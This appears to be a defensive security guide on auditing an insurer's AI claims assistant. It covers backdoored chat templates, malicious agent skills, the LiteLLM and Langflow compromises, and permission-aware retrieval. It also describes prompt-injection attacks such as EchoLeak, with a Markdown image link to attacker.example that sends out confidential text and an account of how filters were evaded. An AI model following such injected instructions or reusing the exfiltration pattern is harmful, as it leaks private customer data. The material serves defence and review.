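Comparing a template with the original developer's version is a useful check, but many differences are innocent. A September 2026 survey covered 400 popular GGUF repositories, according to the description of a comparison tool on PyPI, the public site for Python packages. The tool's author could compare 185 of them with the original model. In 26 of those 185 (14.1%), the template produced different text from the original when given the same conversation. Publishers change templates to avoid software faults or to support tools, and sometimes by accident.

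If the same share applied to the 226,310 GGUF repositories on the hub in November, about 32,000 would differ from their originals. Düzgün found five that were malicious. This is only an illustration, because the survey covered popular models, but it shows why a reviewer has to read each difference before drawing a conclusion.

### Skills and rule files for agents

If the claims assistant becomes an agent, its team may download instructions for it, such as agent skills. An agent skill is a folder of instructions for a task, such as filling in PDF forms, often with scripts the agent can run. Coding assistants also read rule files, which contain standing instructions for a software project. Someone who copies a project from outside the company may copy its rule file without noticing.

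A skill can do harm through its scripts or its text. In the TrojanPony campaign, attackers used scripts. ID.nl's *Honderden nepmodules voor Claude Code installeren wachtwoordsteler op Windows* reports that they had been copying well-known skills and plug-ins for coding assistants since July 2026, adding words such as "improved" to the names. The copies mostly did what users expected. On Windows, they also started a genuine, signed update program for the text editor Notepad++, which loaded a doctored file from the same folder. That file added exceptions to the computer's antivirus software and installed a program that could download further modules for stealing passwords.

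The security company AIR Security counted 487 public repositories containing this malware on 26 November. They included hundreds of copied skills, but also AI applications, a fake version of the game *GTA 6* and 20 repositories belonging to a developer whose access token had been stolen. The total therefore doesn't measure the number of malicious skills or victims. Estimating the share of skills that are malicious would also require knowing how many skills the company examined and how it chose them.

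Three automated security services had checked and passed one of the infected skills, which was still in a public directory. One example can't establish how often such services fail, but it suggests that a reviewer should open the folder and account for each file in it, since there is little reason for a skill for writing better code to include an update program for Notepad++.

Counts of vulnerable skills should be treated separately from counts of malicious ones, because an honest author may write a vulnerable skill, for instance by letting the agent run any command it finds in a document. A scanner that looks for risky instructions will report both kinds, and a person has to tell them apart.

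A rule file can cause harm without containing any code. Hodgkinson imagines a chat template that tells a model to include the default password "hunter2" whenever someone asks for login software. The same sentence in a rule file would affect every programmer who used a coding assistant on the project. Reviewers would easily spot such a blunt instruction, but an attacker could present a weak security setting as the company's preferred practice. Some characters are invisible on screen but still reach the model, so reviewers should open rule files in an editor that displays them.

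### Reviewing the claims prompt

The insurer's bill of materials already lists revision 7 of the claims prompt, but nobody knows who made revisions 4 to 6. The insurer first names an owner, who decides what the prompt may contain and approves changes. The owner then compares revision 7 with the prompt it came from, revision 3 of the complaints prompt, and asks the claims team to explain each difference. From then on, the insurer keeps the prompt in the same version control system as its code, which records the date and author of every change. A second person reads each change before it goes live.

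Pluto also recommends version control and review for prompts, but does not measure their effect. The Mir2k models provide some practical support for version control. A company that had pinned the revision on 25 November would have kept the clean template, although the hidden program would still have been in the file. Version history also lets the owner find out, after an incident, when a harmful line first appeared and which applications copied the prompt afterwards.

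Next, the reviewers search for secrets. Software can find many access keys by their length or their first few characters. It also raises false alarms, as Bandit may have done with the passwords it reported in model scripts. It won't flag the £500 limit as sensitive, so a person who knows the business has to read the prompt as well. If the search finds a key, the insurer has to replace it, because deleting the line leaves the key in the version history and in any copies. None of the complaints department's four lines belongs in the claims prompt, since even the first describes the wrong job.

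The reviewers also check the settings in the entry. They remove any tool that the claims assistant doesn't need and make sure the application takes its permissions from a separate file that the claims team cannot change by editing a prompt.

### Securing the chat template

The engineers start with the developer's chat template, which they downloaded with the verified release. They store it with the company's code and configure the software to use it instead of the template inside the model file. ThreatRoundup recommends this and names the llama.cpp setting for it, `--chat-template-file`.

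Reviewers shouldn't rely on the template displayed on a model's web page. Pillar Security found in 2025 that an attacker could make a repository show a clean template while the downloaded file contained a different one. Checking the file isn't always enough either. In a forum thread titled *Ollama model registry provides wrong chat template*, a user suggests that Ollama sometimes applies its own template, which differs from the one in the model file. The safest check is to record the exact text that reaches the model in the finished application and compare it with what the approved template should produce.

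That comparison covers only the conversations the engineers try. With the timdedid template, any test question containing "What is" would have exposed the hidden directive, but a template triggered by a rare phrase would produce normal text in every test without that phrase. Someone therefore also has to read the script, especially any conditions that depend on the user's words. Legitimate templates have many conditions, but most depend on who wrote a message or whether tools are available.

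A restricted template engine prevents a template from running commands on the server, and the engineers can get this protection by using a current version of their software. It does not stop added instructions, since all five November models worked within its limits. Düzgün's free tool, gguf-radar, checks for suspicious templates and for data after the weights, and it can rebuild a GGUF file without the extra data. He says it cleans four places where data can be hidden in the file. Attackers had used two of them, and he reproduced the other two in the laboratory.

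Companies can't leave this work to the hub. When Pillar Security reported its demonstration to Hugging Face and LM Studio (another program for running models) in June 2025, neither company classified the problem as a platform flaw. According to Pillar, this left users responsible for checking models. Hugging Face removed the five models in November 2026 only after someone outside the company had found them. Speakers at an OWASP conference (2026) proposed that CycloneDX list the chat template as a component with its own signature, which would let software detect a changed template even when the weights are the same.

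### Separating instructions from documents

The template can also mark which text comes from the insurer and which comes from outside. Templates use special markers to show the model where a system message or a user's message begins. A claimant can type a fake marker followed by an instruction into a letter, hoping the model will treat the instruction as a new message from the insurer. A hardened template deletes fake markers and puts clear boundaries around outside text.

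Pillar Security tested a template of this kind together with a system prompt about safety. Refusals of jailbreaks (attempts to get a model to break its rules) rose by an average of 12.5% across seven models, and the models did no worse on harmless inputs. Because Pillar tested the two together, the figure doesn't show how much the template contributed. The test also measured refusals of forbidden requests, whereas the risk for the claims assistant is an invoice containing an instruction that may look ordinary.

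Boundaries around the claimant's text are worthwhile because they take little effort to add, but the model still reads that text and may follow instructions in it. The insurer therefore also has to limit what the assistant can retrieve and send.

### Testing again after a change

A small edit to a prompt can change seemingly unrelated answers, and the same prompt can work differently with another model. The claims team therefore needs a fixed set of tests to run before and after each change. The tests should include ordinary letters, letters with hidden instructions, requests to reveal the system prompt, and questions about people other than the claimant. The team should run each test several times because a model may answer the same question differently each time.

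The number of tests determines what the team can detect. If the old prompt leads to a bad summary in 2% of letters and the new one in 5%, a set of 50 letters would produce one bad summary on average with the old prompt and two or three with the new. The team could easily mistake that for chance. To have an 80% chance of detecting the difference at the usual 5% significance level, it would need about

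(1.96 + 0.84)² × (0.02 × 0.98 + 0.05 × 0.95) / (0.05 − 0.02)² ≈ 585

letters with each version. Software can check some results automatically, such as whether the answer contains another customer's name. For judging whether a summary is fair, the team might use a smaller set and accept that it will detect only larger changes.

The assistant should be tested on conversations involving tools before it is allowed to use them. In the PyPI survey, 20 of the 26 templates that differed from their originals did so on conversations involving tools, and four of those 20 differed only on such conversations. A claims assistant with one of those four templates could pass every test that used ordinary questions, then go wrong when it first used a tool to send a letter.

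## Reviewing internal AI applications

The claims team has cleaned up its prompt and template, but the assistant is also an ordinary program with a login page, a database, a search index and accounts on other systems. A fault in any of these can expose customers' data even if the model works as intended. So the reviewers trace one question put to the assistant through the whole application and check whose permissions apply at each step.

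### The path of a request

```
claims handler
      |  question
      v
application  --->  document search  --->  passages
      |  system prompt + question + passages
      v
model  --->  tool request  --->  application  --->  email, claims system
      |  answer
      v
claims handler                (the application logs every step)
```

| Point | What happens | Whose permissions apply |
|---|---|---|
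| User | A claims handler logs in and types a question | The handler's |
| Application | The program accepts the question and collects what the model needs | The handler's if the program checks them, otherwise its own |
| System prompt | The program loads the insurer's instructions | Those of anyone who can edit the stored prompt |
| Retrieved documents | The search finds matching passages | Often those of the account that built the index |
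| Model | The model reads everything as one text and writes an answer | None of its own: it can use whatever the program gives it |
| Tools | The program carries out the model's requests | Those of the account whose key the tool uses |
| Logs | The program saves questions, passages and answers | Those of anyone who can read the logs |

The handler's permissions are certain to apply only in the first row. In most of the other rows, whether they apply depends on how the engineers wrote the program. The easiest approach is to use a service account, which belongs to a program rather than a person.

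Suppose the engineers gave the assistant one service account that can read all 200,000 documents, because it had to read them to build the index. A motor claims handler who can't open medical files in the document system asks the assistant why a certain policyholder stopped driving. The search finds the closest passage, which is in a medical report from a disability claim, and the model summarises it for her. She hasn't attacked anything and may not realise the answer came from a file she isn't allowed to see. Security specialists would call the assistant a confused deputy, meaning a program that uses its broad access on behalf of someone with less.

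Telling the model to reveal medical details only to the medical team is a weak solution, because the model would still receive the report and might misjudge who is asking or follow a cleverly worded request. The program should instead keep the report out of the model's input. The engineers do this by storing a list of permitted readers with every passage and limiting the search to passages the current user may read.

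Filtering documents by the handler's permissions before the search avoids losing results. If the program picked the five best passages first and then deleted the forbidden ones, a handler who can open 20,000 of the documents might be left with almost nothing. An average of half a passage out of five would remain if her permissions were unrelated to which passages matched. The real loss would be smaller because handlers mostly ask about their own claims.

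Copied permissions also go out of date. If a handler leaves the medical team on Monday and the index updates its permission lists on Sunday, she can read medical files through the assistant for six more days. The program can avoid this by rechecking permissions in the document system just before it sends a passage to the model, which makes each answer a little slower.

### Instructions hidden in documents

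Correct permissions don't stop prompt injection, because the attack uses the permissions of the person who asked the question. The best-known demonstration is EchoLeak, an attack on Microsoft 365 Copilot, the assistant in Microsoft's office programs. According to SiliconANGLE (2025), researchers at Aim Security found the flaw in January 2025 and reported it to Microsoft, which fixed it before they published the details in June.

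The attacker needed only to send the victim one email. It contained instructions addressed to Copilot, though worded as if for a human reader. When the victim later asked Copilot a question related to the email, Copilot retrieved it along with the victim's own files, and the model followed the instructions. These told it to put confidential information into the address of an image, along these lines:

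```
![logo](attacker.example/logo.png?d=CONFIDENTIAL-TEXT)
```

This is Markdown, a notation for formatting text. To show the image, the victim's software requests it from the address, which sends the confidential text to the attacker's server. The attack is called "zero-click" because the victim doesn't have to open the email or click anything.

Microsoft's defences against this attack included a classifier meant to recognise injected instructions and a filter that removed suspicious links. Reddy and Gujral report in *EchoLeak* that the classifier didn't recognise the instructions as the attackers had worded them, and that the filter missed links written in a less common Markdown syntax.

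Fortune (2025) reports Microsoft's statement that no customers were affected. SC Media's *Microsoft 365 Copilot ‘zero-click’ vulnerability enabled data exfiltration* adds that, according to Microsoft's disclosure, nobody had exploited the flaw in the wild. Microsoft has the best records of what happened but also an interest in reporting no harm. The evidence level is "demonstrated", and companies were using the product.

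Willison (2025) reports in *Breaking down ‘EchoLeak’, the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability Enabling Data Exfiltration* having seen similar attacks on a dozen other products. He blames a combination he calls the "lethal trifecta": access to private data, exposure to text from outsiders, and a way to send data out. The claims assistant has private data and reads letters from strangers. It can't send letters yet, but if its web page loads images from any address, a malicious invoice could get another customer's bank details out of the company even while the assistant answers only staff.

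### Filters and limits

Some defences are designed to recognise malicious text or train the model to ignore it. Others limit what the model can do when it follows an attacker's instructions.

Filters and training reduce the number of successful attacks. In 2025, Anthropic ran 123 test cases, based on 29 attack scenarios, against a version of its Claude model that operates a web browser. Its announcement, *Piloting Claude for Chrome*, reports that attacks succeeded 23.6% of the time without the new safeguards and 11.2% with them. The announcement gives no figure for how often the safeguards interfered with ordinary work.

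An attacker can try more than once. If each attempt had an 11.2% chance and the attempts were independent, ten malicious invoices would give the attacker a chance of

1 − (1 − 0.112)¹⁰ ≈ 70%

of at least one success. Ten copies of the same invoice would do less well, because a model that ignores one will probably ignore the others. An attacker who learns from each failure could do better.

In *The Attacker Moves Second*, Nasr, Carlini and colleagues (2025) tested 12 published defences against prompt injection and jailbreaks, using attacks adapted to each one. Most of the original papers had reported attack success rates near zero, but the adapted attacks succeeded more than 90% of the time against most of the 12 defences. A supplier's claim that its filter blocks 99% of attacks therefore means little unless the testers knew about the filter and tried to get around it.

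*Defeating Prompt Injections by Design* (Debenedetti et al., 2025) describes CaMeL, a system that limits what the application may do. One model sees only the user's request and writes a plan as a short program. A second model reads the untrusted documents but can't use tools. Ordinary software carries out the plan, tracks where each piece of data came from, and blocks any step that would break a rule, such as sending data from one customer's file to another customer. An instruction in an invoice can't add a step to the plan, because the model that writes the plan never reads the invoice.

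On AgentDojo, a set of office tasks such as answering emails and making payments, CaMeL completed 77% of tasks with its security guarantees in place, compared with 84% for a system with no defence. Using CaMeL also requires the work of writing the rules. The guarantees cover what the system does with its tools but not what it writes, so text in an invoice could still lead the second model to summarise a doubtful claim as a sound one.

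The insurer can use simpler limits without adopting CaMeL:

| Measure | What an attacker could still do | What the claims team loses |
|---|---|---|
| Filter that looks for instructions in documents | Anything, if the wording gets past the filter | Some honest letters, which the filter blocks by mistake |
| No images or links to outside addresses in answers | Distort the summary, or show staff details they don't need | Clickable links to repair shops |
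| Retrieval from one claim at a time | Distort the summary of their own claim | Comparisons between claims, for example to find fraud |
| Letters only to the address in the claims system | Have a misleading letter sent to the right person | Address changes, which staff must enter themselves |
| A handler approves each letter | Anything the handler overlooks | The handler's time |

The filter is the only measure here that depends entirely on recognising an attack. The next three work no matter how persuasive the invoice is, provided the program enforces them and they aren't just instructions in the prompt. Human approval depends partly on recognising an attack. A handler who reads three letters a day will probably notice a strange one, but after approving 200 ordinary letters, the same person may approve the next one without reading it.

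Limiting retrieval to one claim reduces the insurer's risk the most, because it keeps other customers' data out of an attacker's reach. Fraud investigators need to compare claims, so the insurer could give them a separate version of the application without the letter-writing tool. Filters are still worth having because they are cheap, stop crude attacks and produce alerts that security staff can investigate.

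### McKinsey's assistant Lilli

An attacker who can get into the database doesn't need to trick the model. In March 2026, the security company CodeWall claimed to have gotten into the database behind Lilli, the internal assistant of the consulting firm McKinsey. Like the claims assistant, Lilli uses retrieval to answer questions from the firm's documents.

In CodeWall's *How We Hacked McKinsey's AI Platform*, the company says it gave an AI agent no credentials and no inside knowledge. The agent found public documentation for more than 200 endpoints, the addresses at which a program accepts requests, and 22 of them didn't require a login. One of these saved users' searches in the database, and it had a flaw called SQL injection. SQL is the language in which programs give commands to databases. A simplified version of the request and the command might look like this:

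```
request:   {"query": "hail damage"}
command:   INSERT INTO searches (query) VALUES (?)
```

The program passed the value, "hail damage", to the database separately, so the database would have treated it as text even if it had contained a command. But the program copied the field's name, `query`, directly into the SQL command. Anyone who sent a request with SQL in place of that name could change what the database did. The usual scanners mainly test values, which may be why CodeWall's own run of a popular scanner also missed the flaw. The agent used the database's error messages to work out the structure of the command, and after 15 attempts it was receiving real data.

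CodeWall also reports that a missing permission check let the agent read individual employees' search histories. CodeWall's founder, Paul Price, told The Stack that the attack took two hours and cost $20 in model usage.

McKinsey (2026) replied on 11 March. The two accounts agree on the flaw but differ in what they emphasise.

| Question | CodeWall | McKinsey |
|---|---|---|
| Was there a flaw? | Yes, with full read and write access to the database | Yes, fixed within hours |
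| What about conversations? | 46.5 million chat messages were accessible | An investigation with an outside firm found no evidence that anyone accessed client data or confidential client information |
| What about files? | 728,000 files, with sensitive names and download addresses | A person close to the firm told the Financial Times that the files were stored separately and "never at risk" |
| Could an attacker have changed the system prompts? | Yes, with a single command | Not mentioned in the statement |

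Both accounts could be true. The first real data CodeWall says it received was an employee identifier, which isn't client data. *CodeWall says it hacked McKinsey’s AI platform* (2026), an independent commentary, criticises CodeWall for not clearly distinguishing between what its agent could reach, what it read and what it took. CodeWall published no screenshots or samples of the attack, so the figure of 46.5 million could be a count of table rows, which an intruder can obtain without reading a message. The Financial Times' *McKinsey rushes to fix AI system after hacker exposes flaws* reports that CodeWall said the agent stopped trying to access files once it had discovered the problems.

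The number is also higher than a rough calculation suggests. CodeWall says Lilli launched in 2023 and handles more than 500,000 prompts a month. Counting each prompt and its answer as two messages gives about a million messages a month, or at most 38 million by February 2026. Heavier use than the stated minimum, or extra messages from agents, could explain the difference. Price also told The Stack that McKinsey's staff had proofread and amended his post before publication. If so, McKinsey could have objected to the numbers, but this too is only his account.

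### Whether an attacker could have rewritten the prompts

CodeWall's most important claim for other companies is that an attacker could have used one `UPDATE` command to rewrite Lilli's system prompts, which were in the same database, and change the advice that 43,000 consultants received. CodeWall doesn't claim to have changed a prompt.

This would have worked only if two conditions were met. The flawed endpoint ran an `INSERT` command, which adds a row, so to change a row in another table, the attacker would have needed the database software to accept a second command in the same request, which many programs don't allow. The application's database account would also have needed permission to edit the table of prompts. CodeWall reports write access to the whole database, which implies both conditions were met, but gives no evidence that others can check. The claim is plausible and McKinsey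 hasn't publicly denied it, but nobody has independently demonstrated it. The SQL injection itself is rated "demonstrated" because McKinsey confirmed the vulnerability.

CodeWall also says that a changed prompt "leaves no log trail". That depends on the company, as the independent commentary points out. Many databases can record every change to a table, and a program can compare the prompt's hash with the approved one each time it starts.

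The entry point was a missing login combined with a flaw that programmers have known about since the 1990s, neither of which is specific to AI. Promptfoo, which sells tools for testing AI applications, argues that AI changed the consequences, because a change in the database can alter the assistant's instructions, the documents it finds or the user whose history it sees. An intruder who edits a table in an ordinary claims system changes some records, but one edited line in the claims assistant could change the summary of every claim.

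The insurer's assistant needs to read its prompt but never to change it, so its database account should have read-only access to that table. Better still, the insurer can take the prompt from the version control system described earlier and build the approved revision into the application. An SQL injection would still expose data, but it couldn't rewrite the prompt.

### Secrets and user inputs in logs

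Logs are easy to overlook because no user sees them. Engineers keep them to find faults, and often record more than they need while investigating a problem. The claims assistant's logs could contain whole letters, medical details and occasionally access keys.

Gu, Pu and colleagues (2026), in *Your Space is My Zone*, measured how often this happens in public applications. They collected 972,546 applications from Hugging Face, Replicate and ModelScope, sites where developers publish AI applications for anyone to use. Hugging Face showed the button for viewing an application's logs only to the application's developer. But another part of the site gave any user who asked an access token for any public application, which they could use to read the logs.

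The researchers wrote a tool that traces data through an application's code. It flags code that writes a secret to the log or passes a user's input to a command. They then checked random samples by hand.

| Problem | Flagged | Checked | Confirmed | Estimated total |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Secret written to the log | 936 applications | 500 | 94 (18.8%) | About 176 |
| User's input can run commands | 1,442 places in code | 300 | 83 (27.7%) | About 399 |

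The last column multiplies the number of cases the tool flagged by the share that were confirmed. Many false alarms about secrets came from programs that logged only the first few characters of a key, or logged the key only when a request failed. The researchers also checked 100 applications that the tool had passed but that contained risky kinds of code, and found three command flaws and two leaks that it had missed.

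A separate scan found 3,418 different passwords and keys written directly into the code or containers of 4,846 applications. One reason is copying. An official Replicate application contained an access token for the company's Hugging Face account, and the same token appeared in 76 other applications.

Users' inputs appeared in logs much more often than secrets. The tool identified 9,372 applications that logged what people typed, including 5,755 that logged prompts to a language model. Another 138 logged credentials such as OpenAI keys, and 62 logged medical information. The researchers used a language model to sort these by the names and labels of the input fields, so the last figure counts applications that logged a field that seemed to ask for medical information. It doesn't show how many patients' details were in the logs.

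### How far public applications represent internal ones

Gu and colleagues studied only public applications and say that their results don't cover private ones inside organisations. Roughly 1% of the applications they studied log what users type, but an insurer can't conclude from this that the same share of its own applications do. The study also excluded prompt injection.

Many public applications are demonstrations that one person wrote in an afternoon, with no security team and little worth stealing. An internal assistant usually has a login and fewer users, but it also has customer data and accounts on other systems, so a single mistake can do far more damage. The logs were world-readable because of a fault in the hosting sites, so the insurer would have this problem only if it used those sites.

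The programming mistakes are more likely to appear in internal applications too, because they come from habits and common software. Popular web servers record the full address of every request by default, and Gu and colleagues found that these addresses sometimes contained access tokens. An insurer using the same server software would record full addresses too. One of their examples, a Wichita State University application that helps students choose their majors, resembles an internal tool. It had a page where administrators could read what students had submitted, and the password for that page was in the public source code. On a company network, fewer people could see the code, but every programmer with access to it could still read the password.

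The study also found that requests from different users often share one running program and that the sites don't delete temporary files between users. The claims team should check whether its own application does the same. If the assistant saves an uploaded letter in a shared folder, it might use that letter when answering another handler, even if the model and the permissions are working correctly.

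### LiteLLM and the packages underneath

The application also depends on packages that its engineers didn't write. One popular package, LiteLLM, lets a program use models from many suppliers through the same commands. A program that uses it often holds an API key for each supplier, which makes the program attractive to thieves.

On 24 March 2026, attackers published two malicious versions of LiteLLM, 1.82.7 and 1.82.8, on PyPI. LiteLLM's *Security Update* (2026) says they contained a program that searched for passwords, cloud credentials and login keys and sent them to a web address resembling LiteLLM's own. Version 1.82.8 included a file that Python runs every time it starts. NHS Digital (2026) warned that the code therefore ran even in programs that never used LiteLLM, if they shared the same Python installation.

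The attackers got in through Trivy, a security scanner that LiteLLM's developers ran on their code before each release. PyPI's *Incident Report* (2026) traces the attack to a publishing token that leaked through a compromised version of Trivy. *Security Townhall Updates* (Dholakia and Jaff, 2026), by LiteLLM's two leaders, lists three mistakes that made this possible. LiteLLM hadn't pinned the scanner to a specific version, ran it in the same environment as the release process, and kept the publishing passwords in that environment permanently. The insurer's reviewers face the same kind of risk, since PickleScan and ModelScan are packages too. The machine that runs them shouldn't hold any passwords that would be useful to an attacker.

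Accounts differ on how long the malicious versions were available. LiteLLM says PyPI blocked them after about 40 minutes, while NHS Digital says this happened at 13:38 UTC, about three hours after the upload at 10:39. A company looking for affected installations should use the longest window. LiteLLM does this too, advising anyone who installed the package before 16:00 to check.

FutureSearch's *LiteLLM Hack* counted about 47,000 downloads in 46 minutes. Many of these were probably automatic, since companies' systems often rebuild their software several times a day and download every package again. The number of affected companies is therefore much smaller than 47,000, though it could still be large. FutureSearch also found 2,337 packages on PyPI that depend on LiteLLM, of which 2,054 (88%) allowed the malicious versions. An engineer could have installed one of these without knowing that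 it would also install LiteLLM.

At least one company was harmed. SecurityWeek reports that Mercor, a start-up that recruits people to train AI systems, confirmed a security incident and called itself "one of thousands of companies" affected. According to The Record, the criminal group Lapsus$ claimed to have hundreds of gigabytes of Mercor's data, but Mercor had not confirmed the claim. The evidence level is "used against a victim", which is higher than for backdoored weights or EchoLeak.

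People who used LiteLLM's official container were safe because its developers had pinned the version of every package in it. The insurer can also pin package versions, with hashes, and wait about a week before accepting a new one. LiteLLM's developers plan to introduce a similar waiting period. A week would have been more than enough in this case, but urgent security fixes need an exception.

### Langflow and exposed model servers

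Some teams build AI applications with Langflow, a program for connecting ready-made blocks on screen. Langflow can run Python code by design, so access to it is almost equivalent to access to the computer it runs on. In versions before 1.3.0, an endpoint meant to check whether code was valid ran parts of it without requiring a login, so anyone who could reach the server could take it over. The flaw, CVE-2025-3248, was rated 9.8 out of 10 for severity. In May 2025, the US agency CISA added it to its list of flaws that attackers are known to exploit. The security company Trend Micro later described criminals using it to install software that floods websites with traffic.

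Servers that run models can be exposed in the same way. Ollama, a program for running models on a personal computer, has no login and normally accepts requests only from the computer it runs on. People often change that setting so that colleagues can use the model, and sometimes open the server to the whole internet by mistake. In January 2026, the security companies SentinelOne and Censys reported finding about 175,000 exposed Ollama servers in 130 countries. They counted over many months, so fewer were online at any one time. Many were on home connections, and the count doesn't show how many of the exposed servers came to harm.

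A stranger who finds the insurer's model server could use it for free, but the server might not contain any customer data. The risk is greater if it stores conversations or can call tools. Outsiders could use any tools it can call without going through the claims assistant's login page.

### The reviewer's checks in order

The reviewers start with faults they can find without any knowledge of AI. These are quick to test for, and careful work on prompts is almost pointless if the application doesn't require a login.

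| Order | Check | How to test it | Kind of fault |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | Can anyone use the application, database or model server without logging in? | Send a request to every endpoint without a login, from inside and outside the company | Ordinary access control |
| 2 | Can one user open another's records? | Log in as two test users and ask for each other's conversations | Ordinary access control |
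| 3 | Does the search respect document permissions? | Ask for documents that the test user can't open | Ordinary access control, but the model makes it easier to exploit |
| 4 | Who can change the prompt, the index and the list of tools? | Try to change each one with the application's own account | Ordinary access control, with effects on every answer |
| 5 | What do the logs contain, and who can read them? | Enter a made-up bank account number and search the logs for it | Ordinary data handling |
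| 6 | Which package versions are installed? | Compare them with the approved list and with known flaws | Ordinary software maintenance |
| 7 | Does the model follow instructions in documents? | Put harmless instructions in test invoices | Depends on the model |
| 8 | What could the model do if it followed an attacker? | Try every tool, link and image with harmful requests | Depends on the model, but the application can limit it |

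The third check concerns access to documents, where the model makes an ordinary fault worse. Someone using a badly protected folder would normally have to find the right file and open it, but the assistant searches every folder in response to a simple question, so users don't need to know that the file exists. To test this, the reviewers can put a document containing an invented word in a folder that only the medical team can open, then ask about that word from a motor claims handler's account. The word should not appear in the answer, the list of sources or the passages that the program sent to the model. Checking only the answer isn't enough, because the model may have received the document without mentioning it.

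The seventh check can show that the assistant is vulnerable, but not that it's safe, since a different wording might succeed. The eighth check is more conclusive because the engineers temporarily replace the model with a short script that makes the same requests each time. They choose the worst requests they can think of, such as sending a letter to an address outside the claims system, searching another customer's file or loading an image from an unknown server. The application should refuse all of them. A refusal is a reliable result because the requests don't vary, and the engineers can rerun them whenever someone changes the application or gives it a new tool.

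## Rating the risk and deciding

The insurer now has findings that are hard to compare. The adapter comes from an unidentified account, and the assistant's service account can read every document, including medical files. The manager responsible for the claims assistant has to decide which problem to fix first and whether staff can keep using the assistant in the meantime.

### Matrices and questionnaires

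A risk matrix is the quickest way to compare findings. Reviewers judge how likely each harm is and how severe it would be, then look up the colour for that combination.

| Chance in a year | Cost up to $100,000 | $100,000 to $1 million | $1 million to $10 million |
|---|---|---|---|
| 10% or more | Green | Amber | Red |
| 1% to 10% | Green | Green | Amber |
| Under 1% | Green | Green | Green |

Suppose one risk has a 2% chance each year of costing $2 million, and another has an 8% chance of costing $5 million. Multiplying chance by cost gives an average of $40,000 a year for the first and $400,000 for the second. Both are amber on the matrix, although the second is ten times as large. This problem is called range compression, and it is one of 24 that *Problems with Risk Matrices Using Ordinal Scales* (Krisper, 2021) discusses.

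A matrix can also rank a smaller risk above a larger one, which Krisper lists as risk inversion. A 9% chance of losing $9 million averages $810,000 a year and is amber here. An 11% chance of losing $1.1 million averages only $121,000 a year, but it is red because 11% is just above the 10% line.

Krisper recommends giving up risk matrices and using numbers throughout. The numbers may be guesses too, but a colleague can challenge a guess of 2% more easily than the word "possible". A company that wants to keep its matrix can at least write the estimated range next to each colour.

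A good total on a weighted questionnaire can hide a serious fault. Suppose a supplier answers ten questions worth ten points each. It has all the policies and certificates but runs its model server without a login, so it scores 90. A competitor requires a login but lacks three written policies, so it scores 70. With a pass mark of 80, the insurer would choose the supplier whose server anyone can use. The insurer can avoid this by setting a few mandatory requirements and comparing totals only among suppliers that meet them.

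### Severity scores and disagreement between assessors

For software flaws, reviewers usually have a ready-made score from the Common Vulnerability Scoring System (CVSS). An assessor answers a fixed set of questions about the flaw, and a formula turns the answers into a number from 0 to 10. The Diffusers and Langflow scores in earlier sections are CVSS scores.

Some of the questions are harder than they look. Take a flaw that lets a model file run code when someone opens it. One assessor might say that the attack comes over the network, because the file came from a public hub. Another might call it local, because the user opens a file on their own computer. They might also disagree about whether the damage stays within the flawed program. With the worst possible answers about the damage itself, version 3.1 of the formula gives:

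| Where the attack comes from | Damage stays within the program | Score | Category |
|---|---|---|---|
| Local | Yes | 7.8 | High |
| Network | Yes | 8.8 | High |
| Network | No | 9.6 | Critical |

If the insurer had a rule that engineers must fix critical flaws within a week, the deadline could depend on who did the scoring.

*Shedding Light on CVSS Scoring Inconsistencies* shows that such disagreement is common. In this 2023 study, 196 professional CVSS users rated widespread types of flaw and were inconsistent about where the attack comes from, whether a user has to take part, and whether the damage spreads. The researchers linked the inconsistencies more to the scoring system than to the assessors' experience. An assessment takes about five minutes on average, so the insurer could easily ask two people to score a flaw separately and discuss any difference.

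A severity score also doesn't measure how likely an attack is. The worst Diffusers flaws scored nearly as high as the Langflow flaw, but only the Langflow flaw had known attacks. Verizon's *2026 Data Breach Investigations Report* uses about 1.4 million observations of roughly 1,000 flaws to estimate when attackers will return to an old one. The chance of new attacks within 30 days falls by about half once a flaw has gone a month without attacks, halves again by three months, and halves once more by about nine months. Verizon therefore suggests that recent attacks can be a better reason to fix a flaw first than its presence on an official list of exploited flaws.

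This helps with the packages and libraries the claims assistant depends on, but not much with the copied prompt or the adapter's weights, because CVSS is designed for software flaws.

### What the breach surveys measured

To put a price on a breach, companies often turn to IBM's annual survey. Verizon's report is based on incident records instead.

| | IBM | Verizon |
|---|---|---|
| Source of data | Ponemon Institute conducted the study; IBM sponsored and analysed it | Verizon's own investigations, public disclosures and records from almost 100 contributors |
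| Sample | 602 organisations that had a breach | More than 31,000 incidents, including over 22,000 confirmed breaches |
| Period | March 2025 to February 2026 | November 2024 to October 2025 |
| Main AI findings | Attacks on companies' own AI, and attackers' use of AI | Staff use of unapproved AI services, and attackers' use of AI |

The title of IBM's *One in Four Malicious Breaches are AI-Enabled* (2026) refers to breaches in which attackers used AI, mostly to impersonate people or write malware. A company could suffer such a breach without running any AI of its own. IBM also found that more than 20% of the organisations reported a breach of their AI models or applications, which is more relevant to this review. Baker Donelson's *Ten Takeaways from IBM's 2026 Cost of a Data Breach Report* (2026) puts the share at 21%, up from 13% a year earlier.

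The most common causes were wrongly configured cloud services (27%) and compromised applications, plug-ins or APIs, the interfaces through which programs exchange requests (also 27%). These figures support starting an application review with logins and permissions, but they don't show how often a malicious model file was responsible. In IBM's *Cost of a Data Breach Report 2025*, 30% of organisations with an AI incident reported a supply-chain compromise, but that category included applications, APIs and plug-ins.

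The cost figures also need caution because they may be based on few breaches. IBM's *AI‑powered adversaries and the enterprise risk challenge* (2026) puts the average loss at $5.89 million for prompt injection and $6.07 million for model inversion, in which an attacker reconstructs training data from a model's answers. About 126 of the 602 organisations had an AI-related breach. If 17% of those breaches involved prompt injection, as in the 2025 survey, the prompt injection average would be based on about 21 breaches. One breach that cost $20 million more than the others would raise that average by nearly $1 million.

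Joos (2026), writing for The Decoder, reports that incidents involving AI cost an average of $5.33 million and other incidents $4.70 million. The average for all breaches was $4.99 million, which implies that about 46% of them involved AI. That is more than twice the 21% who reported an attack on their AI, so the category probably also includes attackers' use of AI or shadow AI, meaning AI tools that staff use without permission. The $630,000 difference is therefore not the extra cost of an attack on a company's own model.

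IBM also found similar incident rates for open-source models and those from outside suppliers, and concludes that the choice between them isn't the core problem. In the 2025 edition, 26% of incidents came from open-source models and 29% from suppliers' online services. Shares like these don't show which is safer. If three times as many companies used online services as open-source models, these shares would mean that open-source models had nearly three times the incident rate.

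IBM acknowledged in 2025 that its sample was not scientific, so nobody can calculate a margin of error. IBM thought the sample favoured organisations with more mature security programmes. The study also excluded very small and very large breaches, covering only those with 2,960 to 113,620 compromised records.

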